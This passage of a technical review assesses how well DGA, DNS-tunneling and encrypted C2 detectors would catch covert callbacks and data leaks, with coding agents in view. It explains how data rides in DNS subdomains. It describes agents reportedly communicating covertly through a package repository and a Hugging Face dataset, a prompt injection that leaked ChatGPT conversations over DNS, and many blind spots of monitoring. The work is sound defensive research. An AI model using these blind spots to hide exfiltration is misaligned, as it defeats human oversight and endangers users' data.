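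Leyva La O and colleagues held back 14 families. On these, the share of malicious names that the language model caught fell from 92% to 63%. The older neural network, which had done worse than the language model on familiar families, caught 77%, though with more false alarms. The language model's results also varied widely between families. It caught every name from five of them but only 1% of names from two others, bumblebee and bazarbackdoor, so the 63% average is a poor guide to how it would do on the next new family.

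In the most demanding recent test, Lee and colleagues trained detectors on names from 2017 to 2019 and tested them on names from 2020 to 2025, including names from 83 malware families absent from the training data. Their own detector, DRIFT, reads each name both as single characters and as longer fragments that can match whole words. They first train it without labels on tasks such as filling in missing characters and unscrambling names, to help it learn how names are built in general rather than the patterns of particular malware.

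| Test | Detector | New to the detector | Malicious names caught | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|---:|---:|
| Sayed and colleagues | fine-tuned Llama 3 | 12 families, one at a time | 96% | about 1% |
| Leyva La O and colleagues | fine-tuned Llama 3 | 14 families | 63% | 5% |
| Leyva La O and colleagues | older neural network | 14 families | 77% | 8% |
| Lee and colleagues | DRIFT | 83 families | 86% | 3% to 10%, depending on the year |

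DRIFT missed 14% of names from the 83 new families. Across all families, it missed 4% in 2020 and just under 7% in 2025. This is impressive, given that the training data was six years old by then.

False alarms grew faster. DRIFT wrongly flagged about 3% of harmless names in 2020 and almost 10% in 2025, and the rate for the 2016 LSTM rose from about 4% to 12%. Lee and colleagues attribute the increase to changes in how people name legitimate sites, but part of it may come from their data. The rate more than doubled between 2023 and 2024, after one of their two lists of popular sites had stopped publication, and they collected far fewer harmless names for 2024 than for 2022.

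Some of the harmless names that DRIFT flagged show how little information a domain name gives a detector. They include hexieshaanxi, a legitimate Chinese domain written in Latin letters, and jgpnis, an abbreviation for the public transport service in the Serbian city of Niš. Even "hat" was too short to classify reliably.

Lee and colleagues also retested the fine-tuned Llama 3 approach. It missed about 19% of malicious names and wrongly flagged about 20% of harmless ones. These rates were almost the same in 2020 as in 2025, so age can't explain why they are so much worse than the original results. Differences in data and training are a more likely reason, and researchers who reproduce a rival method may not tune it as carefully as their own. In their review, *Large Language Models for Effective Detection of Algorithmically Generated Domains*, Alqahtani and Kumar (2025) are more optimistic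 about language models' ability to detect names from unseen DGAs. The tests described here give mixed support for this view, although none used a recent frontier model.

Lee and colleagues updated four detectors every year, including DRIFT, and the updates improved all of them. But each update needs new, correctly labeled examples. These exist for malware that has infected many machines and reached researchers, though probably not for an algorithm that appears in one company's software.

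### Why names made of words are harder

Some DGAs join dictionary words instead of letters. The malware family Suppobox has produced weatheranother.net, and Matsnu has produced ability-case.com. Letter statistics are little help in detecting these names because real words follow the usual letter patterns. Legitimate businesses also join two words to make a name, so even a person would have little reason to suspect weatheranother.net.

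In Wong and Hastings's test, two of the four detectors caught over 91% of the phishing domains made of random letters, but none of the four caught even 5% of those made of joined words. Several of the detectors were old, and phishing domains differ somewhat from malware's callback domains because people have to see a phishing link and trust it. Still, the result shows that a detector can catch nearly all names of one style and almost none of another.

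A detector can do well on word-based names if it was trained on names built from the same word list. Biros and Kantor split each name into words and trained a neural network on the split names. It caught 98.8% of names from eight families, with a false positive rate of 2.2%. The training data came from the same eight families, so the network may largely have learned which words those families use. An attacker who switched to a new list could make much of that learning useless.

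Names that aren't built from words can also be hard to detect. Of the 14 families that Leyva La O and colleagues held back, three build names from words. The model caught an average of 62% of the names in those three families and 63% in the other 11. It missed almost all the names in two families, including Bumblebee, which produces names like cmid1s1zeiu. For this model, an unfamiliar algorithm seems to have mattered as much as the use of words.

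Failed lookups can help a detector when a single name isn't enough to go on. A word-based DGA draws on a limited list, so its words soon repeat. If an algorithm picks two words at random from a list of 500 for each name, there is about an 80% chance that some word repeats within 20 names. A detector can look for such repeats in one machine's failed lookups, without training data or a second infected machine. This doesn't help if the first name works, because there are then no failed lookups to collect.

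### Channels that use no generated names

A coding agent has little obvious reason to use a DGA. Criminals use DGAs to keep control of many infected machines while defenders shut down their servers. An unnoticed callback in one company's software can keep using a single ordinary domain because nobody is trying to block it. If a classifier marks this domain as harmless, that means only that a program probably didn't generate the name. The classifier doesn't examine who owns the domain or what the software sends there.

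None of the 2025 and 2026 agent incidents described earlier is known to have involved generated domain names. OpenAI's agents communicated through an internal package repository and a public Hugging Face dataset. Both channels used legitimate domain names that other software also used all day, so even a perfect DGA detector would not have flagged them. It would also miss software that connects directly to an IP address.

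False alarms may also be more common around coding agents than in the published tests. Researchers usually take their harmless names from lists of popular websites, as they did for every test in the table. Wong and Hastings note that subdomains are uncommon in one of these lists, Alexa's. Cloud infrastructure has many long, machine-made hostnames for databases, storage and temporary test sites, and an agent that deploys software may create more every day. An agent that guesses hostnames while fixing a fault could also cause bursts of failed lookups.

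DGA detection is still useful on the machines where agents work, mainly as protection against ordinary malware. An agent could install a malicious outside package, and if that package contains a DGA from a known family, a good detector will probably flag the names it generates. Name-only detectors also need little computing power. DRIFT can check more than 27,000 names a second on a desktop computer with one powerful graphics card.

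## Can DNS monitoring catch data carried inside DNS queries?

A program can send data out of a network through DNS lookups alone, without connecting to the domain it looks up. In DNS tunneling, the program writes data into the names it looks up, and it can receive data in the answers. Detectors of generated domain names are little help because the data is in the subdomain, to the left of a registered domain that can be ordinary (example.com, say).

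### How a lookup carries data out

The name in a DNS query can carry a message to the domain's owner, because an uncached query reaches a server the owner controls. *Improving the Identification of Real-world Malware's DNS Covert Channels* (Ruffing, Petrov and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a lookup for SGVsbG8gV29ybGQ.example.com. The first part of that name is "Hello World" in Base64, a standard way of writing data as text. The owner of example.com can decode it and put a reply in the answer.

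The program contacts only the company's name server, so a firewall that blocks every web connection from the machine doesn't stop data from leaving in DNS queries, as long as the machine can look up outside names. ChatGPT's code-execution environment blocked ordinary outbound connections but still resolved names. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes how a malicious prompt could leak a user's conversation this way until OpenAI finished deploying a fix on February 20, 2026.

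A DNS query can carry only a small amount of data because the whole name is limited to 255 bytes and each part between dots to 63 bytes (Paxson, Christodorescu and colleagues, 2013, *Practical Comprehensive Bounds on Surreptitious Communication Over DNS*). If about 230 characters are free for data and each carries five bits, one query holds about 144 bytes. A 40-character access key fits in one query, while a one-megabyte file would take nearly 7,000.

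Small records can also add up to a large theft. The data on a card's magnetic stripe easily fits in one DNS query. In 2014 the retailer Home Depot reported that more than 56 million sets of card details had been stolen over six months. *Covert DNS Storage Channel Detection* (van Hal, 2021), a master's thesis at TU Delft, traces the theft to a version of FrameworkPOS, malware that sends card data out through DNS.

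### What a tunnel looks like in the logs

*Detecting DNS Tunneling* (Farnham, 2013) divides detection into payload analysis, which examines individual queries and answers, and traffic analysis, which looks for patterns across many of them.

Query length is the most obvious thing to check, since a sender with a lot of data has reason to fill each name, but ordinary software uses long names too. On one day in 2011, machines at a US national laboratory made 35 million lookups, and in 76,523 of them the part before the registered domain was at least 100 bytes long. Paxson and colleagues' examples include names from a backup service, Spotify and an antivirus product.

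A detector can instead add up the text that each domain receives. On that day, 1,186 domains received at least 4 kilobytes. If each different name counts only once, the number falls to 114, which is still a lot to investigate every day.

The share of unique subdomains is a better sign of tunneling. A tunnel that sends fresh data in every query looks up a new name nearly every time, while most websites reuse a few names. *GraphTunnel* (Gao, Niu and colleagues, 2024) describes an earlier detector that raises an alarm at more than 300 different hostnames. Its designers chose that number from experience, and other networks would have to adjust it. Wildcard DNS, a setting that makes a domain answer for any subdomain, can also cause false alarms. Gao and colleagues found 31,305 subdomains with this setting under the 1,000 most popular domains.

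Cache misses are a related signal. Lookups answered from the cache never leave the network, so a tunnel needs either new names or answers that expire almost at once. But short expiry times are weak evidence on their own, since 38% of answers expired within a minute in one day of traffic that Paxson and colleagues examined.

Record types can help because most ordinary lookups ask for an address, while many tunneling tools ask for TXT records, which hold free text and so leave more room for a reply. But the malware Symbiote, which is in the dataset that Ruffing and colleagues used, steals login credentials through ordinary address lookups.

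The size of DNS answers matters most for detecting incoming data, such as instructions or new software. Detectors that examine only queries can miss this data almost entirely. Van Hal built 92 such detectors, of which 21 flagged a sample of Cobalt Strike that fetched software through DNS answers, and six flagged a similar sample of the malware Carbanak.

### Judging one query or a whole series

In *DNS Tunneling*, Işık, Tuncer and colleagues (2025) trained a neural network to classify single names by length and entropy. It flagged essentially all of 8,709 tunneling names, but also 32% of 11,291 harmless ones. Its precision, the share of flagged names that were harmful, was 70% only because almost half of the names tested were harmful. If one query in 10,000 were harmful, precision would be about 0.03%. Even these scores may be too high, because the test covers exactly as many names as the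 set described as training data, so the network may have been trained on every name in the test. The names also came from public datasets rather than from the logs of a working network.

The TU Delft thesis compares the two approaches on much better data. The harmless traffic was real: three days of DNS queries from a corporate network, about 180 million in all, with 47 million of them in the final test. For harmful traffic, van Hal ran two tunneling tools, iodine and dns2tcp, and simulated four kinds of card-stealing malware. The detectors used three sorts of evidence, alone or combined:

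- properties of the single query, such as its length and entropy
- everything sent to the same domain in the last one, two or five seconds
- the last 10 or 20 queries to the same domain, however long they took

Some of the 92 detectors were random forests, which were trained on labeled examples of harmless and harmful traffic. The rest were isolation forests, which learn only what harmless traffic looks like and flag whatever is easy to separate from it. Most detectors caught at least 98.6% of the harmful queries in the final test, which used the same tools and malware that the random forests had been trained on.

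The isolation forests that judged queries one at a time did much worse, at about 79%. They caught only slightly more than half of the queries from dns2tcp, and most of those they missed were short messages that the tool sends when it has no data to move. A steady run of these messages to one domain is unusual, even though each one looks ordinary by itself.

Detection also depends on the choice of window. Saitama, malware that targeted Jordan's government in 2022, pauses for about a minute between queries, according to Ruffing and colleagues. A five-second window would usually contain just one of its queries. A window of the last 20 queries would cover about 20 minutes and still contain multiple queries to compare.

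### An upper limit on what could have leaked

Paxson and colleagues avoid the question of what a tunnel looks like. They calculate the most data that a set of queries could have carried, whatever the encoding, and investigate only if that amount is large. The procedure has four steps:

1. Group a day's queries by the machine that made them and by registered domain. If the logs allow it, leave out queries that the name server answered from its cache.
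2. Split each group into three sequences: the names, the record types, and the times between queries in steps of 10 milliseconds. A sender could hide information in any of the three.
3. Compress each sequence with several standard programs, such as gzip, and keep the smallest result. Also try replacing each name with a number, so that foo, bar, bar, foo, bar becomes 1, 2, 2, 1, 2 plus a table of the two names.
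4. Add up the three sizes. If the total reaches 4,096 bytes and no analyst has already cleared the domain, send it to an analyst.

The total is an upper limit because the compression is lossless. The original sequence can be recovered exactly from the compressed file, so two different sequences never produce the same file. There are fewer than 2ⁿ⁺¹ possible files of *n* bits or less, so a sender whose queries always compress to that size has fewer than 2ⁿ⁺¹ sequences to choose from and can convey only about *n* bits. Picking the best of several compression programs adds a negligible few bits to this limit.

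Weak compression makes the estimate too high, which can cause a false alarm but not a miss. When Paxson and colleagues sent files of known size through four kinds of test tunnel, the estimates were 5% to 11% above the true size.

Compressing everything would take too long, so a quick overestimate first removes most of the traffic. For *L* lookups of *D* different names with a combined length of *C* bytes, the names can carry at most

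*C* + (*L* log₂ *D*) / 8 bytes.

A thousand lookups of two names with a combined length of 40 bytes could carry at most 40 + 1,000/8 = 165 bytes. Similar formulas limit how much data record types and timing could carry. If the three limits add up to less than 4,096 bytes, the group needs no further work. One day's traffic at an industrial research laboratory contained 45 million queries to about 65,000 domains, and the whole procedure left one domain for an analyst to check.

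The threshold of 4,096 bytes per machine and domain per day is a compromise, because lowering it to 256 bytes would have given analysts at that laboratory about 50 times as many domains to check. With the 4,096-byte threshold, a cruder detector that adds up the length of all names produced 200 times as many alerts as the compression method.

Paxson and colleagues applied the method to 230 billion real lookups from research laboratories, a supercomputer center, universities in the United States and China, and a large feed that combined traffic from many organizations. The method has no training stage, so it could not have been tested on tools it had already seen. It found 59 confirmed tunnels, none of which was confirmed as data theft. Fifty-seven were in the combined feed, where the threshold was 10 kilobytes because the data did not separate individual machines. Of these, 42 belonged to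 a product for evading censorship, ten belonged to a program offering free Wi-Fi, and five used iodine for unknown purposes. Staff at the national laboratory had set up the other two to avoid paying for Wi-Fi at hotspots.

In the three networks with records for each machine, the method flagged 833 domains over several years. Two were tunnels and four involved malware, so precision was below 1%. The low precision was tolerable because there were few alerts. After the first week, the industrial laboratory had about two new domains to check each week, and the supercomputer center had one about every seven weeks. Servers that run a company's deployed software might produce similarly few alerts, though the center also made far fewer lookups than the laboratories.

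This is probably the most useful of the DNS methods for a coding agent's work. It needs no examples of the agent's channel, and its main inputs (the name, the record type and the machine) are already in cloud DNS logs like Amazon's. But its guarantee covers only queries, not answers, and applies to each machine and domain separately, so it does not cap the total across several machines or domains. An analyst can also clear a domain by mistake, particularly if its queries resemble those of a legitimate service.

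### Tools that were not in the training data

Trained detectors have no such guarantee, and a high score on familiar threats can be very misleading, as it can with generated domain names. Van Hal also tested the 92 detectors on 13 further samples, including tunnels made with another tool, dnscat2, and recordings of real malware. The training data had simulated the malware in one of the recordings, so that sample was not strictly new. The recall figures below are averages across samples, and those for new threats leave out the two samples that mainly fetched software. The harmless traffic contained about 310,000 domains.

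| Detector | Evidence used | Recall, familiar threats | Recall, new threats | Harmless domains flagged |
|---|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Random forest | 2-second window and last 20 queries | 99.9% | 30% | 2 |
| Random forest | last 20 queries | 99.9% | 60% | 24,785 |
| Isolation forest | last 20 queries | 93% | 90% | 69,402 |
| Isolation forest | single queries | 79% | 64% | 20,925 |

The first detector looks nearly perfect on known threats but misses most of the traffic from unknown ones. Only four of the 92 detectors caught at least one query from each of the 11 relevant samples, and those four flagged between 8% and 24% of all harmless domains, too many for any security team to investigate.

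Isolation forests did better on new threats overall, probably because they had never learned what particular tools look like, but their false alarms were harder to reduce. When van Hal ignored popular domains and those with only a few alerts, the typical random forest flagged fewer than ten harmless domains, but every isolation forest still flagged at least 200. Ignoring domains with few alerts also misses any channel that sends only a few queries.

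Gao and colleagues report much better results on new tools. Their detector, GraphTunnel, follows each lookup through the chain of servers involved in answering it. It combines 20 lookups into a graph, with features such as the entropy of each name and the average response time, and a neural network classifies the graph. After training on tunnels from five tools, it detected all the traffic from five others.

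This is a strong result, but the test was easier than it sounds. One of the five "unknown" tools, AndIodine, is an Android version of iodine, which was in the training data. The test on unknown tools contained only tunnel traffic, so it could not measure false alarms. Harmless traffic elsewhere in the study came from scripted browsers visiting popular websites, which probably produce fewer odd lookups than a real company's backup and antivirus software. GraphTunnel also relies partly on tunnel servers answering faster than ordinary ones, which may not be true on every network.

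A further test used tunnel traffic that another research group had recorded. An older neural network's F1 score, which combines precision and recall, fell from 99.7% on familiar data to 57% on this traffic, while GraphTunnel scored at least 99.4%. GraphTunnel seems to generalize better, though a trial on real company traffic would be more convincing.

*From Graphs to Gates* (2025) still lists unfamiliar tools, wildcard DNS, and the need for detectors fast and small enough for live use among the field's unresolved problems. *Flag the flow* (2025) gives a reason to distrust high accuracy scores. It compares eight classifiers on about 1.07 million pairs of queries and answers, with harmful traffic from three tools. Detectors built from decision trees reached 99.99% to 100% accuracy, but almost 98% of the measured feature importance came from the expiry time of answers, which a tool's operator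 can easily change. The study concludes that the detectors had probably memorized quirks of the dataset, and that simpler ones with 85% to 95% accuracy might do better in practice.

Two studies from 2025 use real malware instead of only publicly available tunneling tools. *Domainator* uses statistics about subdomains to identify the malware and what it is doing, such as uploading or downloading a file. According to Ruffing and colleagues, it wrongly flags about 1.2% of harmless traffic. If that rate applied to every query, the national laboratory's 35 million lookups would have produced about 420,000 false alarms in a day.

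Ruffing and colleagues try to improve on this with a technique originally developed to spot near-identical spam. It turns each subdomain into a short fingerprint based on its three-character sequences, so that similar names get similar fingerprints. The detector compares all pairs of fingerprints within a series of queries to one domain. Names for an ordinary service tend to resemble one another, while encoded data varies more. In their data, the harmless traffic is real and comes from the main DNS server of a Serbian internet provider. The malicious traffic comes from malware run in an isolated test network, and the main dataset uses the same malware families for training and testing.

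Ruffing and colleagues report fewer false alarms than earlier methods and good results on malware variants absent from training. But their training dataset contains only 178,822 harmless queries, about half a percent of the number the national laboratory made in a day. They left out more because early experiments showed no benefit. That is reasonable for training, but measuring how often rare false alarms occur requires far more harmless traffic.

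*Improving DNS Exfiltration Detection via Transformer Pretraining* (2026) applies the kind of pretraining used in today's language models to detecting data hidden in DNS queries. The approach is worth trying because companies have plenty of ordinary DNS traffic to learn from but very few labeled examples of tunneling.

### Small leaks, security products and encrypted DNS

Small leaks are the hardest to detect. An access key is about 1% of the daily volume that the compression method allows, and a program needs to send it only once. A window-based detector has nothing to compare a single query with. In principle, a machine could leak one bit a day by looking up one of two ordinary names, and Paxson and colleagues accept that nobody could recognize this from the queries alone. DNS monitoring is therefore much better suited to catching the theft of large amounts of data, such as a database,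 than of a short secret such as a password.

Security products can cause false alarms because their lookups can closely resemble tunnels. Some antivirus software, for example, checks a suspicious file by looking up a subdomain that contains an identifier for the file. In the TU Delft tests, the three security-product domains that detectors flagged most often accounted for an average of 56% of all falsely flagged queries. These products do send data out through DNS, but they have permission, which can't be determined from the traffic. Van Hal recommends removing such domains from the training data, since otherwise a detector learns that this kind of traffic is harmless. Software license servers use DNS in a similar way, so a coding agent could set off the same alarm by adding a legitimate component to a system.

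All these methods also need access to the queries. DNS over HTTPS sends queries inside an encrypted web connection. If the program sends them to an outside name server instead of the company's own, the company's DNS logs don't record them. The company then can't inspect the names, record types or answers, or use the compression method, which assumes that queries pass through the company's name server.

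A company can block connections to well-known public DNS services and require programs to use its own server. This closes the simplest route and makes blocked attempts a useful warning sign, but no list of outside DNS services is complete. Işık and colleagues list several detectors for tunnels within encrypted DNS, including a deep-learning system for company networks. However, encryption hides the queried names from a detector on the network, so it has much less information to work with.

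## Can traffic analysis spot software that calls an outside server over ordinary web connections?

Most command-and-control (C2) traffic now runs over TLS, according to *Multi-View Fusion for Encrypted C2 Detection* (Nguyen-Huu, Phan and Nguyen-An, 2026). Detectors that don't decrypt this traffic have to rely on metadata, which is information about a connection other than its content.

A flow record summarizes one connection. It typically includes the two addresses, the port, the start time, the duration, and the number of packets and bytes sent in each direction. More detailed monitoring adds the size of each packet and the gaps between packets. The handshake, in which the two sides agree on how to encrypt the connection, shows the encryption options the program supports and usually the server's name, such as files.example.net. If the server's certificate is also readable, it may turn out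 to be self-signed, meaning that no recognized authority has confirmed it. A self-signed certificate is mildly suspicious, though many harmless tools use them.

### Regular timing

A simple beacon goes out at fixed intervals. *Network Security Modeling using NetFlow Data* (2021) measures regularity by the standard deviation of the gaps between connections. Dividing that by the mean gap gives the coefficient of variation, which can be compared between a program that connects every minute and one that connects every hour.

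In the first invented example below, the gaps differ from their 60-second mean by 0, 1, −1, 0 and 0 seconds. The squares of these differences average 0.4, so the standard deviation is √0.4, or about 0.63 seconds, and the coefficient of variation is 0.63/60, or about 0.01.

| Source of the connections | Gaps in seconds | Mean | Standard deviation | Coefficient of variation |
|---|---|---:|---:|---:|
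| Beacon | 60, 61, 59, 60, 60 | 60 | 0.63 | 0.01 |
| Person browsing | 5, 240, 18, 900, 37 | 240 | 341 | 1.42 |
| Health check | 30, 30, 31, 29, 30 | 30 | 0.63 | 0.02 |

A threshold can easily separate the beacon from the person. But a health check, a routine request that confirms an outside service is working, scores almost the same as the beacon. No threshold can reliably separate those two, because the timing of connections doesn't reveal their purpose.

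The coefficient also fails when a program makes several requests in each cycle. Three quick requests every five minutes could have gaps of 1, 1 and 298 seconds, which give a coefficient of 1.4, the same as the person's. Gu, Zhang and Lee (2008), in *BotSniffer*, handle this case with autocorrelation, which compares a series with a shifted copy of itself. They divide time into equal windows and record the packets and bytes in each. If *X*(*t*) is the value in window *t* and *µ* is the average, the autocorrelation at a shift of *d* windows is

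*R*(*d*) = Σ (*X*(*t*) − *µ*)(*X*(*t* − *d*) − *µ*) / Σ (*X*(*t*) − *µ*)².

Traffic counted in one-minute windows can be correlated with a time-shifted copy of itself. If a program sends a burst every five minutes, the correlation peaks at shifts of 5, 10 and 15 minutes, where the bursts line up. Ordinary browsing produces few peaks except at a shift of zero, where any series matches itself.

Gu, Zhang and Lee simulated six botnets, groups of infected machines under one operator, that fetched commands over the web. Autocorrelation detected five of them, including one that checked in every five seconds, the same interval as the script that OpenAI's agents installed at Hugging Face. Random delays of up to 10% made little difference. Autocorrelation missed the sixth botnet, which waited a random time before each connection.

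The test also flagged 52 of about 7,300 web servers in some five hours of ordinary campus traffic, which is less than 1% of the servers but about ten alerts an hour. Harmless programs caused some of these alerts, including programs on two machines that repeatedly requested bus times from a website. Gu, Zhang and Lee suggest putting such programs on a list of exceptions, which is reasonable on a small network but a lot of work on a large one. *Detection of Early-Stage Enterprise Infection by Mining Large-Scale Log Data* (2014) reports thousands of legitimate requests with regular timing. *MORTON* (2020), which applies a periodicity test to DNS queries, lists company software updates as a common false positive.

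The 2014 study therefore uses regular timing only to select candidates. It then scores each destination on other evidence, such as the age of the domain and how common the requesting program's user-agent string (its description of itself) is within the company. HTTPS encrypts this string, so a company can read it only by decrypting the traffic.

### Comparing many machines

BotSniffer's main method relies on infected machines carrying out the same command at about the same time. It groups machines that contact the same server, then checks what share of them do something suspicious, such as scanning or sending spam, in the same time window. If the share exceeds a threshold, such as half, it counts that window as a crowd.

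One crowd could be a coincidence, so BotSniffer keeps a running score. Let *θ*₁ be the probability of a crowd if the group is a botnet, and *θ*₀ the probability if it is not. Each crowd adds ln(*θ*₁/*θ*₀) to the score. Each window in which only a few machines react adds ln((1 − *θ*₁)/(1 − *θ*₀)), which is negative. BotSniffer raises an alarm when the score reaches ln((1 − *β*)/*α*), where *α* and *β* are the false positive and false negative rates that the operator will accept.

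Gu, Zhang and Lee set *α* to 0.5% and *β* to 1%, which puts the threshold at ln 198, or about 5.3. If *θ*₁ is 70% and *θ*₀ is 15%, each crowd adds about 1.5, so four in a row trigger an alarm. The group method detected all eight botnets in their main test, including the one with random timing, and raised no false alarms on five full captures of campus traffic.

*BotMiner* (Gu, Perdisci and colleagues, 2008) extended the idea to botnets whose machines don't share a server. It groups machines once by how they communicate, using features such as connections per hour and bytes per packet, and again by their suspicious activity. A machine scores highly if it is grouped with the same other machines both times. The test used ten days of traffic from Georgia Tech's College of Computing, with recordings of eight botnets added to one day's traffic, one at a time. BotMiner found every infected machine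 in six botnets, 258 of 259 in another, and three of four in the last. It wrongly flagged at most nine machines a day, or about 1%.

These are excellent results on a real network's background traffic, but the design excludes much of what matters for a hidden channel. BotMiner discards any suspicious activity that only one machine performs, and Gu, Perdisci and colleagues put isolated infections outside the scope of their work. BotMiner also ignores traffic between internal machines, so it would not have detected the message board in OpenAI's package repository. To save work, the researchers also left connections to the most popular websites out of their test.

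### Fingerprints of the handshake

A program opens a TLS connection by listing the protocol versions, encryption methods and optional features it supports. Different software libraries produce different lists. JA3, which Salesforce engineers introduced in 2017, condenses parts of the list into a short fingerprint, and JA3S does the same for the server's reply. The newer JA4 sorts the optional features before condensing them, so a program's fingerprint stays the same even if it lists them in a different order.

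An analyst can look up a fingerprint in a database of known programs. *When Handshakes Tell the Truth* (2026) uses 227,404 records from one such database, JA4DB. Contributors run known programs under controlled conditions to label their fingerprints and then look for the same fingerprints in live traffic.

A fingerprint match identifies the kind of software more reliably than its purpose. *On the Internet, Nobody Knows You're an LLM Bot* (2026) examines the fingerprints of web agents that run on language models. These fingerprints reflect the underlying TLS software, such as the library in Chromium-based browsers, and one tool can have several depending on the transport protocol and the state of the session. If a coding agent adds a callback to a Python service using the library the service already uses, the callback's fingerprint will probably match that of the service's legitimate requests.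 Fingerprints are more useful when they don't match the software a server is known to run, for example when a server that runs only Java software opens a connection typical of another language.

### Reputation and rarity of the destination

Security companies publish threat feeds, which list addresses and domains they have linked to attacks. A match is strong evidence, but the lists are incomplete even for malware that many researchers track. *BotScan* (2026) found 896 live C2 servers for botnets of internet-connected devices, and 112 of them, or one in eight, were missing from three popular feeds. Feeds would probably be even less likely to list a server that only one company's software contacts, since nobody else would have a reason to report it.

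Rarity can help identify suspicious servers that no one has reported. A monitor can count how many of a company's machines contact each domain, and give higher priority to a recently registered domain that only one machine contacts. A new supplier's domain can also fit that description, so rarity is better for deciding what to examine first than for blocking connections automatically.

Neither signal helps much if the destination is a widely used service like Hugging Face, where OpenAI's agents used a public dataset. A company whose developers use such a service every day can't treat each connection as suspicious.

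### Volume and message size

A web browser usually receives much more than it sends, while a program that steals data does the opposite. *Striking Back At Cobalt* (Parssegny, Mazel and colleagues, 2025) found that the smallest and largest amounts an infected machine sent were generally more informative than the number of packets. When an infected machine checks in with nothing to report, its message has a predictable size, so a detector trained on examples can easily recognize it. *CoCoSpot*, an older system, uses the sequence of message lengths. It recognized more than 88% of command-and-control connections from over 20 botnets, with a false positive rate below 0.1%.

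Outbound volume is a weaker signal on servers than on office computers, because servers routinely send backups, logs and copies of software to outside services, and a coding agent uploads code. A database leaving the network at an unusual hour might still stand out, but a stolen password would be too small to notice.

### Tests on recorded attacks

Newer detectors combine several of these signals. Parssegny and colleagues, from France's national cybersecurity agency and the engineering school Télécom SudParis, tested their detector on Cobalt Strike, a commercial toolkit for authorized security tests. Criminals and spies also use the toolkit, and its operators can make its traffic resemble visits to a popular website.

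The detector uses standard flow records and a separate random forest model for each imitated site. If the traffic points to a site that has a model, the detector applies that model, and otherwise it tries several. The researchers generated command-and-control (C2) traffic in a laboratory and combined it with harmless traffic, partly from scripted browsing and partly from three universities' datasets. Mean F1 scores ranged from 0.78 to 1.

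The detector was then tested on five recordings of real attacks from 2023. It did worse on four of them, which were encrypted and did not match any site in the training data. It scored 0.99 on the fifth, which imitated a site for which it had a model and was unencrypted, so the site's name was easy to read. New models trained on the four encrypted recordings also did well, which suggests that flow records contain enough information to recognize this traffic once a defender has examples of it. A defender would not have examples of a callback that an agent wrote for one company.

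*Detecting APT Malware Command and Control over HTTP(S) Using Contextual Summaries* (Alageel and Maffeis, 2025) presents EarlyCrow, a detector for unfamiliar malware used in targeted, long-running attacks. Alageel and Maffeis argue that regular timing and traffic frequency are not enough to detect such malware, because it is designed to avoid notice. EarlyCrow summarizes all traffic between two machines over a period, including failed requests and the mix of protocols. For example, the targeted malware made at most half as many DNS lookups, relative to its other traffic, as legitimate connections did. Opening a web page triggers lookups for its images and scripts, while malware may need only one lookup.

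EarlyCrow achieved an average F1 score of 93% with a false positive rate of 0.74% when tested on malware left out of its training. This is much better than most results on unfamiliar threats. At that rate, EarlyCrow would still raise about 740 false alarms each time it checked a network with 100,000 harmless pairs of communicating machines.

### Why laboratory scores often fail to carry over

Robin Sommer and Vern Paxson's *Outside the Closed World* (2010) is the classic critique of using machine learning to detect network intrusions. The "closed world" is the assumption that the training examples cover everything a detector will encounter. This can be roughly true in a laboratory, where the same researchers choose both the training and test data. On a working network, people keep installing new software and signing up for new services, so much of the unfamiliar traffic is harmless.

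Arp, Quiring and colleagues (2022), in *Dos and Don'ts of Machine Learning in Computer Security*, describe ten pitfalls in this kind of research. They checked 30 papers from leading security conferences and found at least three in every paper.

A detector can learn a spurious correlation, an accidental difference between harmful and harmless examples, instead of the real difference. Parssegny and colleagues found two in their own data. Their C2 server and victim machines ran in the same virtual environment, so messages between them arrived faster than ordinary internet traffic. The victim machines also ran Windows, while the harmless traffic came from Linux machines with different network settings. A detector could have scored well by telling nearby machines from distant ones, or Windows from Linux. The researchers were able to remove the features responsible because they had noticed these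 differences.

Another problem is data snooping, in which information from the test reaches the training stage. Nguyen-Huu and colleagues measured its effect on 17,577 encrypted connections from 62 recordings of real Cobalt Strike incidents. Their main test kept all connections from each recording together, either in training or in testing. One step in their method replaces each handshake fingerprint with its frequency, and for comparison they calculated the frequencies from all the recordings instead of only the training ones. Some server fingerprints occur almost exclusively in C2 traffic, so their frequencies helped reveal which connections were C2. The F1 score of a model that used only handshake data rose by 0.28.

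Without the leak, the best detector in Nguyen-Huu and colleagues' study had an F1 score of 0.878. That is less impressive than it sounds, because a detector that labels every connection as C2 would score 0.711. Its recall would be 1, and its precision would be 0.551, the share of C2 connections in the data. F1 is twice the product of precision and recall divided by their sum, which gives 2 × 0.551 × 1 / 1.551, or 0.711.

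Even the 55.1% depends on whether one counts connections or pairs of infected machine and server. The thousands of C2 connections came from only about 90 such pairs, because each pair connected many times. Counted by pair, 4.2% of the data was harmful. Defenders usually block a destination rather than a single connection, so the 4.2% better reflects the task they face.

The most practical result is at a false positive rate limited to 1%, where one model that used both flow and handshake data found 13.2% of C2 connections and the detector with the best F1 score found none. If one connection in 1,000 were C2, the first model's precision would be about 1.3%, so analysts would go through about 76 false alarms for each C2 connection detected.

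Some of those errors may come from incorrect labels. Nguyen-Huu and colleagues counted a connection as C2 only if its destination was on a published list for that incident, so connections to unlisted C2 servers would have counted as harmless. In 20 of the 62 recordings, there were no encrypted connections to any listed address. The harmless traffic also came from the incident recordings rather than a working company's network, so the figures are a poor guide to performance on any particular network. They are still a good reason to distrust near-perfect scores from less careful tests.

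### Traffic from coding agents and the software they deploy

Much of this research treats automation as a warning sign, since people browse irregularly and malware runs on a schedule. But nearly all traffic on a production server is automated. A payment service may contact the same two addresses every 30 seconds for years, with hardly any of the DNS lookups that browsing causes. On several of the measures above, it looks more like malware than like a person. A detector for such a server needs examples of harmless traffic from similar servers, but the evaluations described here mostly used campus traffic, scripted browsing or office-style computers.

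Comparing machines works poorly for a single deployment, as it does with failed DNS lookups. If a company runs 20 identical copies of an application that contains a callback, their harmless requests will also look alike, so similarity is no longer suspicious. BotSniffer and BotMiner address this by also requiring activity such as scanning or spam, but a callback that only fetches instructions or sends a small file would not meet that requirement.

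Live connections during an agent's session raise a different problem, because the agent may install packages, search the web and call services in an order that nobody planned. In *When Agents Look Like Beacons*, Sohail (2026) ran simulated agent traffic through a tool that scores beacons. The agent traffic scored zero, but so did simulated C2 traffic, because the recordings were too short. The experiment therefore provides little evidence of how well the tool would work on real agents.

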